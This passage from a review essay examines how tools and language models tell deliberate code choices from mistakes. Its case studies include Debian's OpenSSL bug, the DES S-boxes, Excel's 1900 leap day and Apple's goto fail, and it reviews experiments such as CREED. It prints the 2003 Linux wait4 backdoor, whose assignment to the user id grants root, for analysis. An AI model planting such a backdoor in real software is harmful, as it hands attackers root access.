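| New miner, balanced | 49 | 107 | 69% |
| New miner, strict | 20 | 1 | 5% |

These are percentages of rules, so they aren't comparable with the precision of MUDetect's warnings. A real rule can still produce false alarms if the checker analyzes the code incorrectly, and Le Goues and Weimer didn't verify every violation. The strict miner also found fewer than a third as many real rules as Weimer and Necula's.

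Weighting probably doesn't explain all of the improvement. Le Goues and Weimer trained their miner on rules that people had already labelled as real or false, so it learned from human judgements as well as from common usage. In a separate test, they gave Weimer and Necula's miner only the most trustworthy quarter of the material. Choosing good code alone saved a lot of reading but did little for precision. The number of real rules fell from 75 to 39 and the number of false ones from 683 to 306, so the share that were false fell only from 90% to 89%. The least trustworthy quarter produced only two real rules.

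When Le Goues and Weimer repeated the comparison on 1.5 million lines of code, 63% of the balanced miner's rules were false, compared with 3% of the strict miner's. The strict miner's one false rule concerned Hibernate, a library for storing data. Under this rule, a program that begins a set of changes must later call `commit`, which makes them permanent. Programs nearly always do this, but they may instead call `rollback`, which cancels the changes. The code that broke the rule was as good as the code that followed it, so weighting couldn't show that calling `commit` was common but not required.

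### Detectors since 2025

Some new detectors still treat rarity as a sign of error. *AFGNN* (Pirapuraj, Mondal and colleagues, 2026) uses a neural network to group similar uses of a function and flags small groups as possible misuses. It had higher precision and recall than MUDetect on MUBench. But precision depends on how common errors are in the code being tested, so this result doesn't show how many false alarms the detector would raise in ordinary code.

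In *API Misuses*, Nielebock (2025) still describes high false alarm rates as the main weakness of existing detectors. He tries using the history of the code instead. One method looks for misuses in the changes programmers make. The other turns developers' past fixes into templates for finding similar mistakes elsewhere. Both had higher precision than existing detectors, and the method based on fixes did better of the two. Past fixes provide evidence that counts of common usage can't, but they help only with kinds of mistake someone has already noticed.

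## Cases where the rare pattern was meant, or the common one was wrong

People sometimes take a deliberate choice for a mistake, or a common practice for a correct one. A few such cases left enough evidence to establish what the makers meant. They show that these errors happen and how much damage one can do, but not how often they happen, because people investigate the cases that did damage or aroused suspicion. Estimating rates requires samples, such as the audit in which a third of the detectors' false alarms concerned code that was uncommon but correct. Investigators settled the cases below using documents, the makers' own accounts and records of who changed what, rather than by counting.

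### The line that Debian removed

Encryption programs need random numbers to make keys that nobody can guess. OpenSSL, a widely used encryption library, collects unpredictable data in a *pool* and calculates random numbers from it. Debian, which distributes a version of Linux, maintains its own copy of the library.

In 2006 Kurt Roeckx, who maintained Debian's copy of OpenSSL, was testing programs with Valgrind, a tool that checks for memory errors as a program runs. Valgrind warned that OpenSSL was using uninitialised memory, which a program has reserved but not yet filled. Using such memory is normally a mistake, because it still holds whatever was there before. *Lessons from the Debian/OpenSSL Fiasco* (Cox, 2008) traces the warnings to two identical lines, `MD_Update(&m,buf,j);`, each of which mixes a block of memory into the random number generator's pool.

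OpenSSL's developers had used uninitialised memory on purpose in at least three places. The leftover data might be slightly unpredictable, and adding predictable data to the pool does no harm. In one place a comment told readers to use the whole block even if the program had filled only part of it. One of the two lines that Valgrind's warnings led to also had a switch to turn it off, with the comment "purify complains", because a similar tool called Purify gave the same warning.

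The two lines looked the same but did different jobs, though it seemed reasonable that if OpenSSL could do without one, it could do without the other. The line with the switch was in the function that supplies random numbers, where it mixed in whatever the caller's memory already contained. The other was in the function that adds fresh random data to the pool. When Roeckx disabled both, the pool received almost nothing, though OpenSSL kept raising its estimate of the pool's randomness. Only the process ID, a number that Linux gives each running program, was still slightly unpredictable. SSH, a program for logging in to other computers, could then generate only 32,767 different keys of a given type and size (about 15 bits of unpredictability), so an attacker could try every key.

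Before removing the lines, Roeckx wrote to OpenSSL's mailing list on 1 May 2006 that he had no idea what effect removing them would have. Someone with an OpenSSL address replied that uninitialised data added "not much" randomness and favoured removing the lines if it helped with debugging. That was true of the uninitialised data, but the same code also added the real randomness. Cox thinks the developer probably answered without looking up the code. One of Cox's readers objected that the reply might have approved only a temporary change for debugging, and Cox conceded that it could be read that way.

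The faulty version appeared in September 2006. Cox couldn't think of a plausible test that would have caught the problem, because the numbers from any single run still looked random, even though different computers often produced the same ones. According to a chat log that one of Cox's readers posted, Luciano Bello found the error by accident when he needed many prime numbers and kept getting duplicates. Debian's Florian Weimer (2008) announced the error on 13 May in *New openssl packages fix predictable random number generator* and blamed a change that only Debian had made. People had to install the corrected library and also replace every weak key they had made in the meantime.

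Princeton CITP's *The Debian OpenSSL Bug* considers whether the change was sabotage and concludes that it was an accident, partly because Roeckx later became Secretary of the Debian Project. That is weak evidence, as some readers replied, since a patient infiltrator would also seek a position of trust. The mailing list is better evidence, because Roeckx publicly described the change there beforehand and admitted his doubts to the people best placed to object.

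He also had a sensible motive for silencing the warnings. One of Cox's readers pointed out that a tool that prints many harmless warnings is useless for finding real errors. But acting on a false alarm can do more harm than wasting the five minutes it takes to read.

### Unexplained tables in a cipher

Unlike OpenSSL's developers, who left a few comments, the designers of the Data Encryption Standard (DES) kept their reasons secret. An IBM team developed the cipher around 1974, with technical advice from the US National Security Agency (NSA), and it became a national standard in 1977. The government published the whole method, including eight tables called *S-boxes*, each of which replaces six bits with four, but it didn't publish how the team had chosen the tables' contents.

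By 1976 a group that included the Stanford cryptographer Martin Hellman had worked out several of the rules the S-boxes followed, but not what the rules were for. Many people suspected a trapdoor, a hidden weakness that would let anyone who knew about it read other people's messages.

Don Coppersmith (1994), in *The Data Encryption Standard (DES) and its strength against attacks*, gave the team's reasons. The S-boxes protected DES against *differential cryptanalysis*, in which an attacker has the target machine encrypt pairs of messages that differ in chosen bits. DES combines message bits with key bits by an operation called XOR, which gives 1 if two bits differ and 0 if they match. For messages a and b and a key k,

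(a XOR k) XOR (b XOR k) = a XOR b

The key cancels out, so the attacker can know the difference between the two inputs to an S-box without knowing the key. If that difference often leads to a particular output difference, the attacker can predict how differences will change through the cipher's 16 rounds. Pairs that behave as predicted then reveal parts of the key.

The team chose S-boxes that make these predictions unreliable. For any input difference, the 64 possible inputs form 32 pairs, and at most eight of them may produce the same output difference. A prediction about one S-box is therefore right at most a quarter of the time. Other rules make differences spread to more S-boxes from round to round.

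The best remaining attack involves three neighbouring S-boxes in every second round. The prediction holds for all three with a probability of 7/32 × 4/32 × 5/32, or about 0.0043. It has to hold in six rounds, which happens about once in 160 trillion attempts. Eli Biham and Adi Shamir, who published the attack in the early 1990s, estimated that they would need about that many messages.

IBM's designers of DES knew about differential cryptanalysis by 1974. After discussions with the NSA, they kept their design criteria secret because publishing them would have revealed an attack that works on many other ciphers. People would keep quiet about a hidden strength for much the same reasons as about a hidden weakness, so the designers' silence was poor evidence of a trapdoor, with a likelihood ratio probably close to 1.

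Coppersmith helped design the S-boxes and acknowledged having strong opinions about DES, so he wasn't a neutral witness. But readers could verify most of his account. Anyone can check the published tables against his criteria, and Biham and Shamir had already independently found how much work the attack required.

Coppersmith's account explains the structure people had noticed, but it can't rule out every other weakness, and he describes one himself. Mitsuru Matsui had just developed *linear cryptanalysis*, which needs less text than the older attack and doesn't require the attacker to choose the messages. One of the team's criteria helped against it. A stricter version would have helped more, but as far as Coppersmith could remember, the team hadn't used one. He still considered the new attack impractical.

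### A day that never existed

Microsoft Excel stores dates as numbers, starting with 1 for 1 January 1900. It assigns 60 to 29 February 1900 and 61 to 1 March. But 29 February 1900 never existed, because a century year is a leap year only if it is divisible by 400.

In 1992, Joel Spolsky, who worked on Excel, noticed the extra day and took it for a bug, as he recounts in *My First BillG Review* (Joel on Software, 2006). His colleague Ed Fries told him it was deliberate. Excel had to open worksheets from an older program, Lotus 1-2-3, which counted the same extra day.

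Microsoft's *Excel incorrectly assumes that the year 1900 is a leap year* describes the error and explains why the company hasn't corrected it. A correction would shift almost every date in existing worksheets by one day. Leaving the error affects only the day of the week for dates before March 1900, which few people use. Excel correctly treats 2100 as an ordinary year, so its programmers evidently knew the rule for century years.

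The Lotus programmers' intention is less certain. Fries guessed that they saved memory by checking only the last two binary digits of the year, which show whether it is divisible by four. That test is always right from 1901 to 2099. Microsoft also states that treating 1900 as a leap year made leap years easier for Lotus to handle, but neither account comes from Lotus. Copying usually weakens the evidence that a programmer meant something, but Excel's programmers copied the extra day on purpose, so it could have been a mistake in Lotus and still be a deliberate exception in Excel.

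A checker that compared Excel's calendar with those of other programs would be right to report a deviation, but a tool that automatically repaired it would damage millions of dates. The designers of Microsoft's Basic programming language avoided including a false date by starting their count one day earlier, so their numbers agree with Excel's from 1 March 1900 onwards.

### An intruder's equals sign

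In November 2003 these two lines appeared in a copy of the Linux kernel's source code:

```
if ((options == (__WCLONE|__WALL)) && (current->uid = 0))
        retval = -EINVAL;
```

They look like an error check in `wait4`, which programs use to wait for something to happen. The first condition tests for an unusual pair of options. The second seems to test whether the user's number is 0, which belongs to "root", who is allowed to do anything. But the code uses `=`, which assigns a value in C, instead of `==`, which compares two. *The Linux Backdoor Attempt of 2003* (Freedom to Tinker, 2013) explains that this turns anyone who calls the function with those options into root. The assignment also evaluates to 0, which C treats as false, so the error on the second line never occurs.

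Programmers often type `=` when they mean `==`, so the line alone could look like a mistake. Larry McVoy, whose company ran the system that stored the kernel's code, overlooked the missing equals sign.

The change records were much more revealing. Linux's developers kept their master copy in a system called BitKeeper, and McVoy's company exported it to a second system, CVS, for people who preferred that. McVoy reported in *BK2CVS problem* (2003) that somebody had changed the CVS copy directly. Every exported change had a number linking it to the master copy, but three entries for this file had none. They listed the author as David Miller, the developer who had corrected Engler two years earlier, but Miller denied making them. There were also signs of an attempted break-in. One entry had the message "Oops, I worked on the the wrong file", as though someone were correcting a mistake.

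McVoy's company found the change because it compared the two copies every night, and he removed it within a day. Linus Torvalds, who leads the kernel's development, said the change couldn't have reached an official release because nobody merged code from the CVS copy.

Developers also looked for signs of intent in the code. One noted that the extra parentheses around the assignment prevent a compiler warning. But they prove little, because C wouldn't accept the assignment there without them, as a reader of Freedom to Tinker's article pointed out. Another reader argued more convincingly that the code would be pointless as an error check, since it would forbid a harmless pair of options, and only for root. By Dennett's assumption of good design, the code makes much more sense as a back door.

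A search for rare patterns might have flagged the line. Richard Johnson, another participant in the mailing-list discussion, suggested scanning the kernel for every use of `current`, the record that holds the user's number, and ignoring the expected ones. He added that a clever programmer could evade the scan by reaching the record through a hard-to-follow pointer.

Whether the line was a deliberate exception depends on who counts as its maker. The intruder intended it and would presumably have left it there, but the kernel's developers didn't and removed it at once. Someone looking for errors can ignore the difference, because the developers would want either a slip or a back door removed. But someone who reads the code as a record of what the developers wanted would attribute a stranger's purpose to them, and the author's name in the log would seem to confirm it.

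The intruder's identity is still unknown, and according to Freedom to Tinker, only a confession or an incriminating document is likely to reveal it. Schneier (2013), in *Defending Against Crypto Backdoors*, reviews several old security flaws for signs of tampering and mostly judges how likely tampering was. He thinks the Linux change was probably deliberate and the Debian one probably wasn't. He writes only that DUAL_EC_DRBG, a suspect random number generator, "may or may not have been a backdoor".

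Change records help less when the attacker has permission to make changes. In *Fifty Years of Open Source Software Supply Chain Security*, Cox describes how Andres Freund noticed in March 2024 that a login program on his computer was using more processor time than usual, and traced the cause to liblzma, a compression library. Someone who had spent about two years earning the right to maintain the library had put a back door in it, so its records showed an authorised change by a trusted colleague. The extra processor time led Freund to the problem, but he had to read the code to learn that it was deliberate.

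### A duplicated line at Apple

A similarly small change disabled a security check on Apple's phones and computers until February 2014. The code was supposed to confirm that a website was genuine. It ran a series of steps, each followed by an instruction to jump to the end if the step had gone wrong. In one place the instruction appeared twice. In simplified form, the code read:

```
if (this step went wrong)
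    goto fail;
    goto fail;
```

The condition applies only to the first `goto fail`. The second is indented as if it belonged to the condition too, but C ignores indentation, so the program always ran it and jumped to the end. Because no earlier step had failed, the program reported success without checking the website's signature. An attacker who controlled the network could therefore impersonate a bank.

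Apple had published an earlier version of the code that contained the line only once. It removed the duplicate and said the fix restored missing validation steps. It didn't explain how the second line got there, and some people suspected sabotage. A pasting or merging accident is more likely, and Apple's prompt correction is consistent with one. But the evidence is weaker than for Excel's extra day, which the makers themselves explained.

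Counting would have helped little here, because `goto fail` was among the most repeated lines in the function, and a language model with a cache would have assigned a high probability to another one. The contradiction was a much better clue. The code after the second jump, which included the signature check, could never run, so the error can be found by assuming, as Engler and colleagues do, that programmers don't write pointless code.

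### When most apps are wrong

Following a common convention was an error in the caller that mishandled `seg_alloc`, but with encryption the common practice itself can be wrong. *An Empirical Study of Cryptographic Misuse in Android Applications* (Egele, Brumley and colleagues, 2013) checked 11,748 Android apps that used encryption functions and found that 10,327 (88%) broke at least one of six basic rules.

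One rule forbids ECB mode, which encrypts each block of a message separately, so identical blocks stay identical after encryption. Under a standard definition of security, an attacker who submits two messages and gets back one of them encrypted must be unable to tell which it is. With ECB, the attacker can tell by submitting one message made of two identical blocks and another made of two different blocks, then checking whether the encrypted blocks match. This proves that ECB fails the definition, so the rule would be right even if every app used ECB.

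Many programmers may have used ECB without choosing it, because both Java and Android defaulted to it when they asked for the AES cipher without naming a mode. Egele and colleagues assume that people who encrypt data want to protect it, which seems reasonable. If so, many of these common uses of ECB are mistakes that the library's designers made easy.

Whether a majority vote would go wrong depends on how many apps break each rule, which the 88% alone doesn't show. If each app had a 30% chance of breaking each of the six rules, independently of the others, 88% would break at least one, yet 70% would follow any given rule. A tool that learned one rule at a time would then get all six right. Help Net Security's *Popular Android apps are rife with cryptographic vulnerabilities* gives some of the per-rule figures from a test of 1,780 popular apps by researchers at Columbia University, who ran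 the apps and recorded how they used encryption.

| What the researchers found | Apps | Share |
|---|---|---|
| At least one of 26 rules broken | 1,780 | 100% |
| Unsafe random number generator | 1,775 | 99.7% |
| Broken hash function | 1,764 | 99.1% |
| CBC mode, which is unsafe in some settings | 1,076 | 60% |
| Fixed key written into the app | 820 | 46% |

A majority vote among these apps would treat the five without an unsafe generator as deviant. It would still be right about fixed keys, but only narrowly. Feichtner's *A Comparative Study of Misapplied Crypto in Android and iOS* cites a similar figure of 82% for iPhone apps and describes correct use as "rather the exception than the norm".

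But breaking a rule doesn't always make an app insecure. A predictable random number is harmless if it only decides which picture to show. Wickert, Baumgärtner and colleagues (2022), in *To Fix or Not to Fix*, cite studies that found misuse in 87% to 96% of Android apps using encryption, but point out that those studies didn't examine whether the findings were valid or how serious they were. The studies also counted whole apps, so an app that uses a function correctly 50 times and wrongly once counts as breaking the rule. A detector that learns from individual calls would get 50 correct examples and one wrong one from the same app.

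Li, Wang and colleagues (2026) give a newer count in *A Measurement Study of Cryptographic Misuse in Embodied AI Mobile Applications*. Their tool reported 12,975 misuses in 507 Android apps that control robots, drones and similar devices. When they checked a sample by hand, about 81% of the reports were correct, which suggests roughly 10,500 real misuses, or 21 per app. This average doesn't show how many of the apps were affected, and apps that control robots may not be typical.

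Li and colleagues attribute much of the misuse to engineering constraints rather than random errors. Some developers send video unencrypted to avoid delays, or write a fixed key into the app so that the robot works without an internet connection. These are deliberate exceptions to good practice that have become common. Other apps inherit outdated encryption from components made by the same suppliers, so one old decision is repeated across many brands.

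Even deliberate choices may not be what the makers would want on reflection. Li and colleagues found a fixed key in an app for a Unitree Robotics robot dog and showed that an attacker could use it to recover the owner's Wi-Fi password. When they reported this, the company acknowledged the risk and began working on a fix.

Looking for odd code would catch only some unsafe cipher settings. In *From base cases to backdoors*, Olaiya and Nadkarni (2025) collected 118,749 calls that select a cipher in apps for connected household devices. About half of the calls gave the cipher's name as text, which is the conventional way to do it. But some conventional-looking names lead to unsafe settings. At least 1,487 calls named `AESWrap`, which uses the unsafe ECB mode by default.

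Olaiya and Nadkarni also found ten calls that fetched the name from a separately compiled part of the app, which checkers rarely examine. All ten were misuses, though far more unsafe calls looked ordinary. Fetching the name this way slows the program down and has no obvious benefit, and they see this as a sign that developers were evading detection. If so, the strange code was deliberate as well as wrong.

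Records of fixes can also mislead, though they are usually good evidence of a mistake. *Tracing Cryptographic Agility in Android and iOS Apps* cites 2019 work by Gao and colleagues, who expected to find developers updating their apps to correct misuse. Instead, most of the updates that removed a misuse seemed to do so unintentionally, and later updates brought it back.

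## Experiments with language models that read intent from code

Tools that count patterns can't use the comments, emails and makers' own accounts that people read to settle the Debian, DES and Excel cases. Large language models can read such material along with the code. But they learn by predicting the next token in huge collections of text and code, so they may reproduce common practice even where a program makes clear that its author meant something else. Since 2023, several experiments have tested whether the models follow common practice or the author's intent.

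### Swapped names

Python programmers use `print` to display a value and `len` to get the length of a list or a piece of text. They can also redefine these names. After the line `len, print = print, len`, each name refers to the other function, so a programmer who wants to display the length of x has to write `len(print(x))`. This looks wrong, but anyone who has read the first line can work out that it is right.

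*The Larger They Are, the Harder They Fail* (Miceli-Barone, Barez and colleagues, 2023) tested whether language models could adjust when the names of two functions were swapped. The researchers took 1,000 functions from Python projects on GitHub, a site where programmers share code, and put a line before each that swapped the names of two built-in functions it used. They gave each model this line, the function's name and a description of what it did, then compared the probabilities the model gave to two versions of the remaining code. One was the original, which the swap had made wrong, and the other exchanged the two names to match the swap.

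Every model gave the wrong version the higher probability in every case. In three families, Meta's OPT and OpenAI's GPT-3 and InstructGPT, the larger models favoured the wrong version more strongly. Larger models are usually better at predicting ordinary code, and here the ordinary code was wrong. But size made little difference among the CodeGen models, which specialise in code, and the larger of two Codex models did better than the smaller one. Each family had only a few sizes to compare.

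The researchers couldn't get probabilities from chat models, so they showed the models both programs and asked which was correct. Two of Anthropic's Claude models chose correctly 10–18% of the time, and GPT-3.5 and GPT-4 less than 4% of the time. Random guessing would have scored about 50%, but the models consistently picked the familiar program, even though the first line of the code set up a deliberate exception. All of these models date from 2023 or earlier, so their scores don't show what current models can do.

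### Mistakes that models repeat

Few programmers swap `len` and `print`. In *Large Language Models and Simple, Stupid Bugs*, Jesse, Ahmed and colleagues (2023) used real mistakes instead. They collected 16,899 bugs from Java projects, each of which developers had fixed by changing a single statement. For each bug, they had every model continue the code leading up to it, then compared the result with both the buggy statement and the fixed one.

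Codex, the model then behind the programming assistant Copilot, wrote the known bug 4,452 times and the known fix 2,267 times. In the other 10,180 cases it wrote neither, and about 90% of the sample that the researchers read from these were wrong. Other models also produced more bugs than fixes. Size helped the CodeGen models, whose ratio of bugs to fixes fell from 1.94 for the smallest to 1.30 for the largest. The models in *Model See, Model Do?* (2026) also tended to write the buggy version.

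The researchers tested Codex only at places where a person had already written a bug, so the two-to-one ratio doesn't mean that Codex usually wrote bugs. Bugs of this kind occur about once in 1,600 lines. Whatever misled the person, such as two variables with similar names, was probably still in the code that Codex received.

Codex gave the bugs it repeated and their fixes about the same probability, so cross-entropy couldn't have distinguished them. These bugs had also lasted longer in the original projects, where developers made a median of 265 recorded changes before fixing them, compared with 106 for the bugs Codex avoided. This agrees with Ray and colleagues' finding that long-lived bugs look ordinary.

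Jesse and colleagues then gave the models more information about what the programmer wanted. They had another model summarise the corrected code in a comment, and they inserted that comment before the place where the bug had been. Because such a comment might reveal the fix, they also tried comments that summarised the buggy code. The table gives the results for Codex.

| Comment added | Bugs | Fixes | Bugs per fix |
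|---|---|---|---|
| None | 4,452 | 2,267 | 1.96 |
| Summary of the buggy code | 6,072 | 3,880 | 1.56 |
| Summary of the corrected code | 5,329 | 5,149 | 1.03 |

Even a misleading comment improved the ratio. The researchers suspect that any comment makes the code resemble the well-documented programs in the training data, which tend to be more reliable. If so, that part of the improvement came from a norm in the training data. The further drop from 1.56 to 1.03 must come from what the comment conveyed about the programmer's intent. The other models they tested did not improve just because a comment was present, and misleading comments made their ratios worse.

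### Actual and expected behaviour

A *test* runs a piece of code on a chosen input and compares the result with an *assertion*, which states what the result should be. An assertion is a small specification, so its author has to know what the code is for. Older programs that generate tests instead run the code and record whatever it returns as the expected result, so if a bug makes that result wrong, the assertion requires the wrong result.

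Konstantinou, Degiovanni and Papadakis (2024), in *Can we find bugs using LLM-generated oracles?*, tested whether language models do better. They showed models a Java function, a test and a correct assertion, and asked whether the assertion was correct. They also asked about correct assertions after planting a bug in the function. The right answer was still yes, because a bug doesn't change what a function is supposed to do. The table shows how often the models answered yes when they could also read the function's documentation and the code around it.

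| Model | Correct code | Buggy code | Drop in percentage points |
|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-3.5-turbo | 44% | 37% | 7 |
| GPT-4o-mini | 60% | 47% | 14 |
| DeepSeek V3 | 55% | 39% | 16 |
| Codestral | 81% | 72% | 9 |
| GPT-5-mini | 92% | 65% | 27 |

All five models rejected more correct assertions when the code was buggy. In one case the altered function returned −2, and a model rejected the correct assertion because the function "is expected to return -2". Warning GPT-4o-mini that the code might contain a bug didn't change this tendency.

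GPT-5-mini, a later model that reasons before it answers, had the best score on correct code and also the largest drop. One explanation is that a model better at working out what code does is also more easily misled when the code is wrong. Still, it accepted about two-thirds of the correct assertions that contradicted the code, so it wasn't judging assertions only by what the code did. Codestral's high scores are less impressive than they look, because it also accepted about half of the wrong assertions when the code was correct.

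The experiment's measure of intent has a weakness. The correct assertions came from a test generator that recorded what an earlier version of the code did, and the researchers assumed that this version had no bugs. Their "expected behaviour" is therefore the earlier version's behaviour, which is a reasonable substitute for intent if that version was right.

Names mattered, as they had for Engler and colleagues. Konstantinou and colleagues replaced informative names in 1,000 developer-written tests with generic ones, so that `shouldThrowForExistingPath` became `test0` and `path` became `var0`. GPT-4o-mini's accuracy fell from 62.5% to 47.1%, and Codestral's from 88.6% to 84.9%. The tests worked exactly as before, so the models must have inferred the developers' intent partly from the names.

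Developers also have models write whole tests, often for code that nobody has checked. In *On the Risks of using LLM-Generated Tests for Regression Testing*, Charoosaei, Richter and Papadakis (2026) planted small faults in 145 real changes to three Python libraries, SciPy, Qiskit and pandas. They kept only faults that the project's own tests missed and that some other test could detect. Claude Haiku 4.5 then wrote a test for each faulty version without seeing the correct one.

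Depending on the library, 8–17% of the tests enforced the fault, passing on the faulty code and failing on the correct code. Only 2.4–4.8% revealed it. The rest gave the same result on both versions. In SciPy, for example, one fault reversed a check so that ordinary calls to a function caused an error, and the model wrote a test that required the error, which a person would probably have questioned.

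Part of the gap between enforcing and revealing comes from the procedure. Like existing tools of this kind, it had the model revise each test, over up to six turns, until the test passed on the faulty code. A first draft that correctly exposed the fault would therefore have been treated as needing repair. The figures are good evidence of what such tools produce, but weaker evidence of what the model would have inferred if its tests had not been required to pass.

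When the researchers followed the tests through later changes to the libraries, 83–91% still enforced their faults at the end. A developer who later corrects such a fault will see a test fail and may conclude that the correction was wrong. The tests could also mislead anyone trying to infer intent from the code. A model derived them from the faulty code, so they add no evidence of what the programmer wanted beyond the code itself, even though they look like a separate statement of it.

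### Two identical error messages

In these experiments the models mostly received code and answered directly. CREED, the tool with which Liu and Böhme revived belief inference, makes a model work through the programmer's assumptions first. It examines one function at a time and uses a single *prompt*, the text that tells a model what to do. The prompt sets out four steps:

1. Identify the actions in the function, from small operations such as following a pointer to the purpose of the function as a whole.
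2. Infer what the developer believed when writing each action.
3. Judge whether each belief is reasonable.
4. Derive the conditions under which it would fail.

The model then reports a *finding* for each belief that is unreasonable or that could fail in a way that matters for security, with an explanation of the cause and the circumstances. The main example is a login function from a program called PolarLearn. In plain words, it works like this:

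```
1: look up the user with this email address
2: if there is no such user, answer "invalid credentials"
3: hash the password that the visitor typed
4: if it matches the stored hash, log the visitor in
5: otherwise, answer "invalid credentials"
```

The important action is giving the same answer for an unknown address and a wrong password. A more specific message would help honest visitors more, so the vague one probably has a purpose. CREED infers that the developer believed an outsider couldn't tell the two cases apart. It judges this belief reasonable, because hiding which users exist is standard security practice.

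The fourth step reveals the flaw, which is that the program hashes the password only when the account exists. Hashing converts the password to a scrambled form that the program can compare with the stored one. This takes time, so a visitor who enters a real address waits longer for the error message than one who enters an invented address. An attacker with a list of addresses could time the responses and learn who has an account.

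CREED didn't need to count how other programs handle logins, because the two identical messages were evidence of what this developer wanted. Someone might repeat a message only to save effort, so the evidence isn't conclusive and this is a MAY belief. But the developers later changed the function to remove the flaw, which suggests that they cared about hiding who their users were.

In the second example, the belief itself was wrong. A function in PublicCMS, a system for running websites, cancelled a pending payment if the payment belonged to the right site. CREED inferred that the developer thought this check was enough to authorize the cancellation, and judged the belief unreasonable because one user of a site could then cancel another user's payment. Unlike the login function, which failed to do what its developer intended, the payment function probably did what its developer intended,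 but not what they would have wanted if they had thought about other users.

### Fifty recent vulnerabilities

Liu and Böhme tested CREED on 50 randomly selected functions from 45 projects. Each function contained a security flaw that became public between September 2025 and March 2026. The underlying model, Claude Sonnet 4.6, had finished training before then, so its training data is unlikely to have included the disclosures. A finding counted as a match only if its explanation agreed with both the published description of the flaw and the fix. Another model judged the findings first, and the researchers checked every match it accepted.

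They compared CREED with four other methods that used the same model. They also ran every method on the corrected version of each function, to see whether the report of the flaw disappeared.

| Method | Flaws explained | Findings | Findings per flaw explained | Flaws reported only before the fix |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| CREED | 39 | 310 | 7.9 | 33 |
| Extended reasoning without the four steps | 34 | 384 | 11.3 | 26 |
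| Prompt for step-by-step analysis | 27 | 141 | 5.2 | 27 |
| Several agents that debate each report | 21 | 69 | 3.3 | 20 |
| Model combined with fixed rules | 1 | 8 | 8.0 | 1 |

For 33 of the 50 functions, CREED reported the flaw in the original version but not in the corrected one, so these reports evidently depended on the flaw rather than the general look of the code. CREED still reported six flaws after developers had fixed them.

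CREED's lead of five over extended reasoning could be luck because the test used only 50 functions, but CREED also came first when the researchers switched to another model, DeepSeek V4 Pro. Each part of the method that they tested seems to help. CREED explained 30 flaws without the step that identifies actions, and 33 without either of the last two steps.

The steps are useful partly because they define what counts as a flaw. In *BUGSCOPE*, Guo, Wang and colleagues (2025) asked Claude 3.7, without giving it such a definition, to find possible divide-by-zero errors in a short piece of code. It reported 11, of which 10 were false alarms. When they told it to report only cases with explicit evidence, it reported none and missed the real bug.

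Their own tool derives guidelines from a past bug report. Under one guideline, if a programmer tests whether a number is at least 0, then 0 must be a possible value, and dividing by the number later is suspicious. This is belief inference too, although the researchers don't call it that. Using such guidelines, the tool found 23 real divisions by zero in 12 other projects and raised only five false alarms.

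Liu and Böhme also considered whether an ideal checker could have found each of the 50 flaws using a general pattern, like Engler's rule templates. They concluded that no such pattern exists for 21 of them, because each depended on who was allowed to do what, what a value meant, or whether a check was good enough. CREED explained 15 of the 21, including the login flaw.

### What surrounding code and local rules can settle

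Most of CREED's 310 findings didn't match the known flaw, but some could still be correct, since a function can have more than one flaw. The researchers checked the first finding for each function by hand. Of these 50 findings, 23 matched the known flaw and 14 described other real flaws, 11 of which developers had already fixed. The remaining 13 were false alarms, so the precision was 74%.

In 10 of the 13 false alarms, CREED correctly identified what would cause trouble, but other code prevented it. Either the function's callers had already made the necessary check, or the function called another one that did. CREED was given only the one function, so it couldn't detect these checks. PR-Miner had the same problem with functions that correctly left a step to their callers. In the other three, CREED missed a safeguard in the function itself. Giving the model more of the program might remove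 many of these false alarms.

CREED's precision of 74% isn't comparable to the 7.4% that Amann and colleagues measured for detectors that learn from common usage, because every function in CREED's test contained at least one flaw. Most functions in ordinary code have none, so a larger share of CREED's findings there would be false. Agents that search live projects face this problem.

CREED missed 11 flaws. It failed to identify the relevant action in three cases, inferred the wrong belief in one and misjudged a belief in another. In another case, it found the flaw but left it out of the final report. The judging model rejected two correct explanations, so CREED actually explained 41 flaws.

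Avoiding the last three misses would have required knowledge of the particular application. One of these functions checked that users had permission to share files, but not that they had permission to download the file, which this application also required for sharing. Another application might deliberately let people share files they can't download, for instance so that an assistant can forward confidential documents without being able to open them. Neither the code nor general knowledge of security can show which rule the owners wanted. Liu and Böhme conclude that the tool needs the application's own security policy.

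CREED judges beliefs against "standard security practice". It has no written list of such practices and relies on what the model learned in training. This standard is therefore another corpus norm, though it probably comes from manuals, expert advice and reports of past attacks as well as from code.

Such a norm can be a better guide than a count of programs. Most Android apps in Egele and colleagues' study broke at least one basic rule of encryption, but textbooks explain why the rules matter. A model that has learned from those explanations can favor the rules even though most of the apps break them. Knowing the reasons for a rule also makes it easier to tell when it doesn't apply.

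Expert advice can also be mistaken or out of date. Security experts long recommended making people change their passwords every few months, and many now advise against it. Developers may also depart from standard practice on purpose. Suppose a website tells visitors when an email address has no account, because many of them forget which address they used. The different error messages show that the owners aren't trying to hide who has an account, but standard practice counts this as a flaw. CREED would probably report it, because although its second step tries to establish what this developer believed, its third compares that belief with what experts generally recommend.

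### Turning comments into conditions

Researchers have used language models to turn a developer's description of a function into *postconditions*, statements that must be true whenever the function finishes. A computer can check a postcondition each time the function runs.

*SPECMIND* (Le, Pham and colleagues, 2026) gives the example of a function that returns the greatest number that occurs in a list at least as many times as its own value, or −1 if there is none. For the list 1, 2, 2, 3, the answer is 2. When a model had only one attempt, it wrote a postcondition requiring the answer to be −1 or a positive number from the list. That condition is true but would allow many wrong answers.

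SpecMind gives the model a function's description and code, and lets the model try out postconditions before submitting one. After a submission, SpecMind reports whether the postcondition held in every test and what share of deliberately broken versions of the function it rejected. In one example, the model produced a complete postcondition on its fifth attempt. On 164 programming problems, SpecMind scored 99.4% for correctness and 89.6% for completeness.

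"Correctness" here means agreement with the code's behaviour in tests. The code in this collection is a reference solution, so agreement is a good sign. But if the code had an undiscovered bug, the same feedback could lead the model to drop the postcondition that exposed it, much as the revision procedure did with Claude's tests.

A postcondition that rules out very little can also pass a check easily. *Path2Spec* (Huang, Sun and colleagues, 2026) reran an older tool called SpecGen, which keeps revising its specifications until a verifier can prove that the code satisfies them. Between 13% and 33% of the specifications that passed had no postcondition or one that was always true.

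*SpecProbe* (Zhang, Wang and Zhai, 2026) avoids both problems to some extent. Its model receives the function's description and an outline of the surrounding code, but not the instructions inside the function, so it can't copy a bug from them. If the resulting postcondition fails when the code runs, SpecProbe reports the disagreement to a developer rather than asking the model for a revision, because the fault could lie in the code, the description or the postcondition. Zhang, Wang and Zhai criticise SpecMind's approach because revising a postcondition to fit the code can hide a real conflict with the documentation.

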